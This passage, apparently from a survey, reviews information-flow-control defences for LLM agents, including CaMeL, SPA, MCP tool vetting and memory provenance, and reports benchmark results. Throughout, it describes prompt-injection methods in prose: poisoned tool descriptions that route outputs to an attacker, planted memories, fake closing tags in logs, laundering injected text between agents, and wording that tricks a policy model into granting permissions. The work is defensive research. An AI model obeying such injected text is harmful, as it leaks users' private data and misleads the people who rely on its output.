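A side channel carries information through behaviour that a system's labels don't cover. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026), in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, report that CaMeL's developers demonstrated two such channels in their own system. One used an indirect dependency between values, and the other an error that an attacker could trigger. The developers also discussed a timing channel, which their implementation reduces.

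A monitor's refusals can reveal information to the agent. In an example from *Causality Laundering* (2026), a monitor refuses to let an agent read a file because the agent lacks permission. The agent can conclude that the file exists, and an injection can make it pass this on. An application could prevent this by giving the same answer for forbidden and missing files. It could also label the refusal as secret, so that later calls inherit the label.

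*Actions Speak Louder than Words* (2026) points out that an agent's legitimate actions on the web may also reveal private information it has read, even if it never transmits the data. Suppose an agent has read in the user's mailbox about an operation, and the user asks it to find a hotel. If it searches for rooms near a particular clinic, the hotel website's owner can guess the reason. A system that tracks how secrets influence decisions could block the search, but that rule would also block most useful browsing once the agent had read the mailbox.

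The paper also cites studies that inferred private information from the length and timing of a model's responses and from the size of network packets. Labels inside the agent can't control what someone observes on the network.

One possible response is to limit how much information can leave. *An Application-Layer Multi-Modal Covert-Channel Reference Monitor for LLM Agent Egress* (2026) describes software that tags sensitive values when they enter the system and checks for them in outgoing data. It also keeps a running total of how much information could have left, because it can't detect a secret that the model has encoded in an unfamiliar way.

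For example, a choice among 16 web pages can carry log₂ 16 = 4 bits, so a budget of 40 bits allows ten such choices. That budget would prevent the leak of a whole 16-digit card number, which takes about 53 bits, but not of a four-digit code, which takes only about 13. A budget therefore works best for large secrets.

Timing is harder to control. The same paper cites research showing that random delays and adaptive padding still leak information, and that only sending at a constant rate defeats a determined analyst. An email agent would have to send messages on a fixed schedule, including dummy messages when it had nothing to send.

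### Documents with the wrong label

The theorems about flow control assume that each source starts with the right label. Narisetty and colleagues argue that every system they surveyed under-specifies how to assign these initial labels, and they expect deployments to fail at this step.

An application may label a company's internal knowledge base as trusted because the documents are on the company's own servers. Customers or contractors who can edit those documents can then add text that the application also labels as trusted. Dehghantanha counts the software that indexes a company's documents as part of the trusted computing base, meaning the components whose compromise undermines the system's security. A planted document can stay in the index until someone asks a question that retrieves it. Retrieval can also break confidentiality if the software returns documents that the user isn't allowed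 to see.

The application could label each page by who edited it instead of where it is stored. If a label lists everyone who may have written the page, one outside edit makes the whole page untrusted. An employee could then review the edit and endorse it, but this would be a lot of work on a busy wiki.

Some documents mix text from several sources. Suppose a colleague forwards the outsider's Project X email with a short note at the top. An application that labels emails by sender will treat the whole message as trusted, including the outsider's request to forward private data. If the planner may read trusted emails, the injection reaches it with a trusted label, and the monitor will accept the recipient the planner chooses.

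The application could label the quoted text in a colleague's email separately, but it can find that text only if the email program marks it, and pasted text may have no mark. It is safer to treat every message that might contain outside text as untrusted, but that would include many ordinary emails from colleagues.

Labels can also disappear when one agent passes work to another. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) tested a system in which each agent runs CaMeL separately. In one case, an orchestrating agent copied text from a website into its instructions for an agent that posts to Slack. The Slack agent's planner treated the whole message as trusted and added the injected action to its plan. Every successful attack on this system followed this general pattern, which the paper calls boundary laundering.

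A second version of the system sends instructions and data through separate channels, so website text never reaches the receiving planner as an instruction. No attack succeeded against this version. It still failed some harmless tasks, some because its plans were fixed in advance and others because of limits on what agents could send each other.

### Poisoned tool descriptions

A planner reads the descriptions of its tools before it reads any email. The Project X example labels these descriptions trusted and public, which is reasonable if the developer wrote them. But many agents use other people's tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting models to external tools and data.

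*When MCP Servers Attack* (2025) explains that a model needs at least each tool's name, description and input format to choose a tool and fill in its arguments. An attacker can exploit this by writing a description that instructs the model to call the tool after every other tool and pass it their outputs for a "security check". The attacker can also imitate the name and description of a legitimate tool so that the model picks the wrong one.

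*MCPGuard* (2025) describes an example disclosed by the security company Invariant Labs. A tool that appeared to supply daily trivia instead caused the user's chat history to be sent to an attacker's phone number.

Checking a tool once is not enough, according to *MCPThreatHive* (2026), because MCP has no way to tie a description to a fixed version. A server can pass an audit and change its descriptions later. An application could store a cryptographic fingerprint of each approved description and ask for a new review if the fingerprint changes. This check wouldn't detect a change in the tool's behaviour if the description stayed the same.

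The flow rules can still help after a tool's description has misled the planner. If the developer limits a new tool to public data, the monitor will block private emails from reaching it, whatever its description. But a tool that needs private data can misuse that data after receiving it.

ACE avoids the problem by keeping the planner from reading descriptions of installed tools. Later tests in SPA show that a similar method can greatly reduce the number of tasks an agent completes.

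### Memory without a record of its origin

Many assistants save information in one session and use it in another. *MemoryDojo* (2026), a benchmark for attacks on agent memory, describes this with two functions:

Mₜ = U(Mₜ₋₁, τₜ) and cₜ = ρ(Mₜ₋₁, xₜ).

Mₜ is the memory after session t, and τₜ is the record of that session. The function U updates the memory, for example by extracting facts or merging notes. Before each session, ρ retrieves the saved context cₜ that seems relevant to the new task xₜ. In the benchmark, the attacker adds text once, in an early session, and the test is whether that text affects a later session.

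To keep the labels correct, U must process labels as well as text. If it merges the user's words with a sentence from an outsider's email, the new note needs the join of both labels. If U saves only the text, the next session has no record that part of the note came from an outsider. A single label for the whole memory would be safe, but one session with an untrusted email would make all of it untrusted, which is label creep across sessions.

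Attackers can often get false information into an assistant's memory. *Hidden in Memory* (Pulipaka, Hlebik and colleagues, 2026) found that text planted in sources such as documents and web pages made assistants save invented facts about the user. The success rate reached 99.8 per cent with GPT-5.5 and 95 per cent with Kimi-K2.6. These figures measure how often the assistant saved the false memory, and a later session would still have to retrieve it and act on it.

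*From Untrusted Input to Trusted Memory* (Dash, Ge and colleagues, 2026) found that agents designed to save and retrieve memories more readily were easier to exploit. It also reports that existing defences against prompt injection do not cover these attacks.

### SPA: labels across several requests

*SPA*, published in August 2026, presents a system that keeps labels attached to stored data. In its main example, a user asks an agent on Monday to fetch an invoice from a company called Acme and save the details. On Tuesday, the user asks the agent to pay it. An attacker has put a different account number and a malicious instruction in the invoice. SPA handles the two requests as follows:

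1. On Monday, the planner writes a complete plan before any tool runs. The plan uses a small language with six kinds of step, including tool calls, conditions and loops.
2. A checker follows the labels through the whole plan, including both branches of every condition. If a flow into a tool breaks the policy, SPA rejects the plan. If the problem is only an item meant for the user's screen, SPA blanks out that item and keeps the rest.
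3. Ordinary software runs the accepted plan and saves each result in three parts: the value, its label and a description.
4. On Tuesday, the planner sees the description but not the value or the label. The description gives the result's format, what it represents and why the agent fetched it. Monday's planner wrote the last two parts without seeing the invoice.
5. The planner writes a new plan with a step that retrieves the invoice. The original label returns with the value, so the checker treats the account number as untrusted.

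The malicious instruction never reaches either planner. If the payment tool requires trusted arguments, the label also prevents it from accepting the attacker's account number. But the same requirement blocks payment of a genuine invoice, because that account number also comes from an untrusted document.

SPA queries the planner only once per request. Unlike CaMeL, it has no automatic retry loop, so if the checker rejects a badly written plan, the request ends without the planner getting feedback or a second attempt.

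SPA's developers tested it on AgentDojo's 97 tasks and on a version that splits each task into two to five requests. They used GPT-5.4 nano, a small model, and an attack whose author knows which tools the malicious action needs. The task figures come from runs without an attack, and the attack figures from 949 attacked runs per row and format:

| Planner | Flow checks | Tasks completed, one request | Attacks successful, one request | Tasks completed, several requests | Attacks successful, several requests |
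|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Reads tool descriptions | off | 53.0% | 0.4% | 62.5% | 0.3% |
| Reads tool descriptions | on | 29.0% | 0.0% | 35.3% | 0.2% |
| Doesn't read tool descriptions | off | 14.1% | 0.0% | 12.6% | 0.0% |
| Doesn't read tool descriptions | on | 6.7% | 0.0% | 9.7% | 0.0% |

Hiding stored values from the planner only slightly reduced the share of tasks with several requests that it completed, from 65.9 per cent when it could read the values to 62.5 per cent when it saw only descriptions. With the flow checks on, later plans retrieved a suitable earlier result in 89.9 per cent of cases where one existed, or 73.4 per cent if we also count cases where the earlier request had failed to save a result.

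The flow checks were much more disruptive, stopping about 45 per cent of the runs with several requests, mostly because a plan passed untrusted data to a tool that required trusted data. Hiding the tool descriptions forced the planner to invent the tools it needed, and in about three-quarters of runs the software couldn't match them to installed ones.

The security results are weak evidence for the checks because the attacks hardly ever succeeded without them. Only 0.6 per cent of attacks succeeded even when the planner could read stored values. SPA's developers acknowledge that the attack barely tests delayed injections. The 0.2 per cent in the table is probably too high, since AgentDojo counted two runs as successful attacks even though SPA had rejected their plans.

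According to one passage in the paper, the checks reduced attack success by 25 to 35 percentage points in three environments, but in the paper's own results, no attack succeeded in those environments even without the checks. The reported drop may be in completed tasks rather than successful attacks.

### Harm within permitted flows

Even with perfect tracking and correct labels, an attacker can do harm through flows that the policy permits. In the Project X case, suppose that the planner never reads the emails, that the email tool requires a trusted call and recipient, and that the body may be untrusted. An outsider's email could then have these effects:

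| Effect of the outsider's email | Result under the flow rules |
|---|---|
| The assistant forwards a private message to the outsider | Blocked, because the call and the recipient would depend on untrusted text |
| The summary contains a false figure or leaves out a delay | Allowed, because the body may be untrusted |
| The summary persuades the manager to approve a payment | Allowed, because the manager's decision is outside the system |
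| The user asks the assistant to pay an invoice, and the email supplies a false account number | Blocked, unless the program endorses the number |
| The summary fails and the manager receives nothing | Allowed, because no flow rule requires a task to finish |

The quarantined model reads the outsider's text and genuine emails in one stream, so it can still confuse their roles, as the models in the probe experiments did. Flow control doesn't reduce this confusion. Its guarantee covers what the software does with the model's output, which stays labelled untrusted however convincing it sounds.

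*Poisoning the Watchtower* (2026) measured how injections affect summaries of security logs. One injection placed a fake closing tag in the log, followed by a verdict that nothing was wrong. Against simple defences, it distorted 96 per cent of summaries. These summaries left out the attack in the log, described it in milder terms or concluded that no action was needed, but none explicitly called the log harmless.

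Restricting the model to fixed output formats reduced the rate to 38 per cent, but the model could still choose a misleading option. Security logs differ from office email, so the rates may not carry over to the Project X assistant. An injection there could similarly make the model omit a missed deadline, and the manager couldn't detect the omission from the summary alone.

The application could summarise each email separately, name its sender and link to the original, which would let the manager check important claims. It could also leave outsiders' emails out of the summary, but then the manager would miss genuine news from suppliers and clients.

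The flow rules treat genuine and false account numbers alike, with or without endorsement. Garby and colleagues note that an agent could tell the two apart only by judging whether the document's contents look suspicious. That is the unreliable kind of inspection flow control tries to avoid. A company could instead compare the number with a supplier record it had already verified.

Text can also mislead the person who reads it. Narisetty and colleagues report that CaMeL's developers explicitly exclude such attacks from what the system is meant to prevent, and warn that the problem will grow as people act on more text from agents. An application can display the untrusted label beside the summary and disable its links, but the manager may still believe a false statement.

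Strict checks can make it easier for an attacker to stop a task. SPA ends a request when a value doesn't fit the required format, so a single email can block the whole summary by making the quarantined model return a malformed answer. Processing each email in a separate call would limit the damage to that email. The application should then tell the user which email it left out, since an attacker might otherwise use the failure to hide something.

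### Who writes the policies, and how often are they wrong?

Someone has to write a policy for each tool, deciding, for example, that the email tool needs a trusted recipient but not a trusted body. The SPA paper warns that an incorrect policy can reject safe plans or allow unsafe ones.

*Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026) examined who writes these rules in 13 research papers and 14 policy layers in products. Eight of the papers and 11 of the product layers used policies fixed before deployment. Developers could write rules that software enforces reliably. End users mostly wrote instructions in plain language, such as the CLAUDE.md files for Claude Code, and relied on the model to follow them. Five of the product layers depended on the model following such instructions, which an injection can override.

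A user who wants an enforceable rule needs programming skills or administrator rights. In the Project X case, the user knows who should receive the summary, but a developer who has never met the manager may have to write the policy.

Language models could draft the rules, but their drafts need checking. In *Structured Decomposition for Reliable LLM-Generated Access Control Policies* (2026), a model wrote ordinary access-control rules in a single attempt. Of the policies meant to forbid an action, 62.5 per cent were wrong, and some passed every syntax check but forbade nothing. Of the policies meant to give access only to a resource's owner, 60 per cent lacked the necessary condition.

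These figures describe the baseline that the paper's method is supposed to improve on. They don't cover flow rules or measure how often people make mistakes. The closest evidence for flow policies is the review of Santos-Grueiro's first set, which found 18 gaps in policies for 24 sinks.

*ActGov* (2026) combines a model with a solver, a program that checks logical conditions. The model drafts rules from tool descriptions, records of harmless tasks and earlier successful attacks. The system adopts the draft only if the solver finds no violation of a fixed set of security requirements. The solver can't check a requirement that nobody wrote down. *ToolGuardian* (2026) similarly describes its own rules as a specification, not a proof that the policy is complete. It recommends deliberately changing rules to see whether the tests detect the change, and using independently written test scenarios.

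If a model updates the policy while the agent works, an attacker can target that model. Progent, a system that checks each tool call against a list of permissions, can use a model to widen the list after reading tool results. Narisetty and colleagues wrote injections that presented a malicious action as harmless and already authorised, so that this model would permit it. They tested the attack on 24 AgentDojo tasks in three environments, using the small model Qwen2.5-7B for both the agent and the policy:

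| Condition | Attacks successful | Tasks completed under attack |
|---|---|---|
| Standard attack without Progent | 25.8% | 45.2% |
| Standard attack with Progent | 4.2% | 27.1% |
| Adapted attack with Progent | 2.6% | 25.8% |

The adapted attack did no better than the standard one. Narisetty and colleagues suspect its reassuring wording also made the agent less likely to carry out the malicious action, so the result may reflect a weak attack. They work for LaunchSafe, a company that builds tools of this kind, and the study has not been peer reviewed. They plan to test next whether an attack can succeed using only actions the policy permits.
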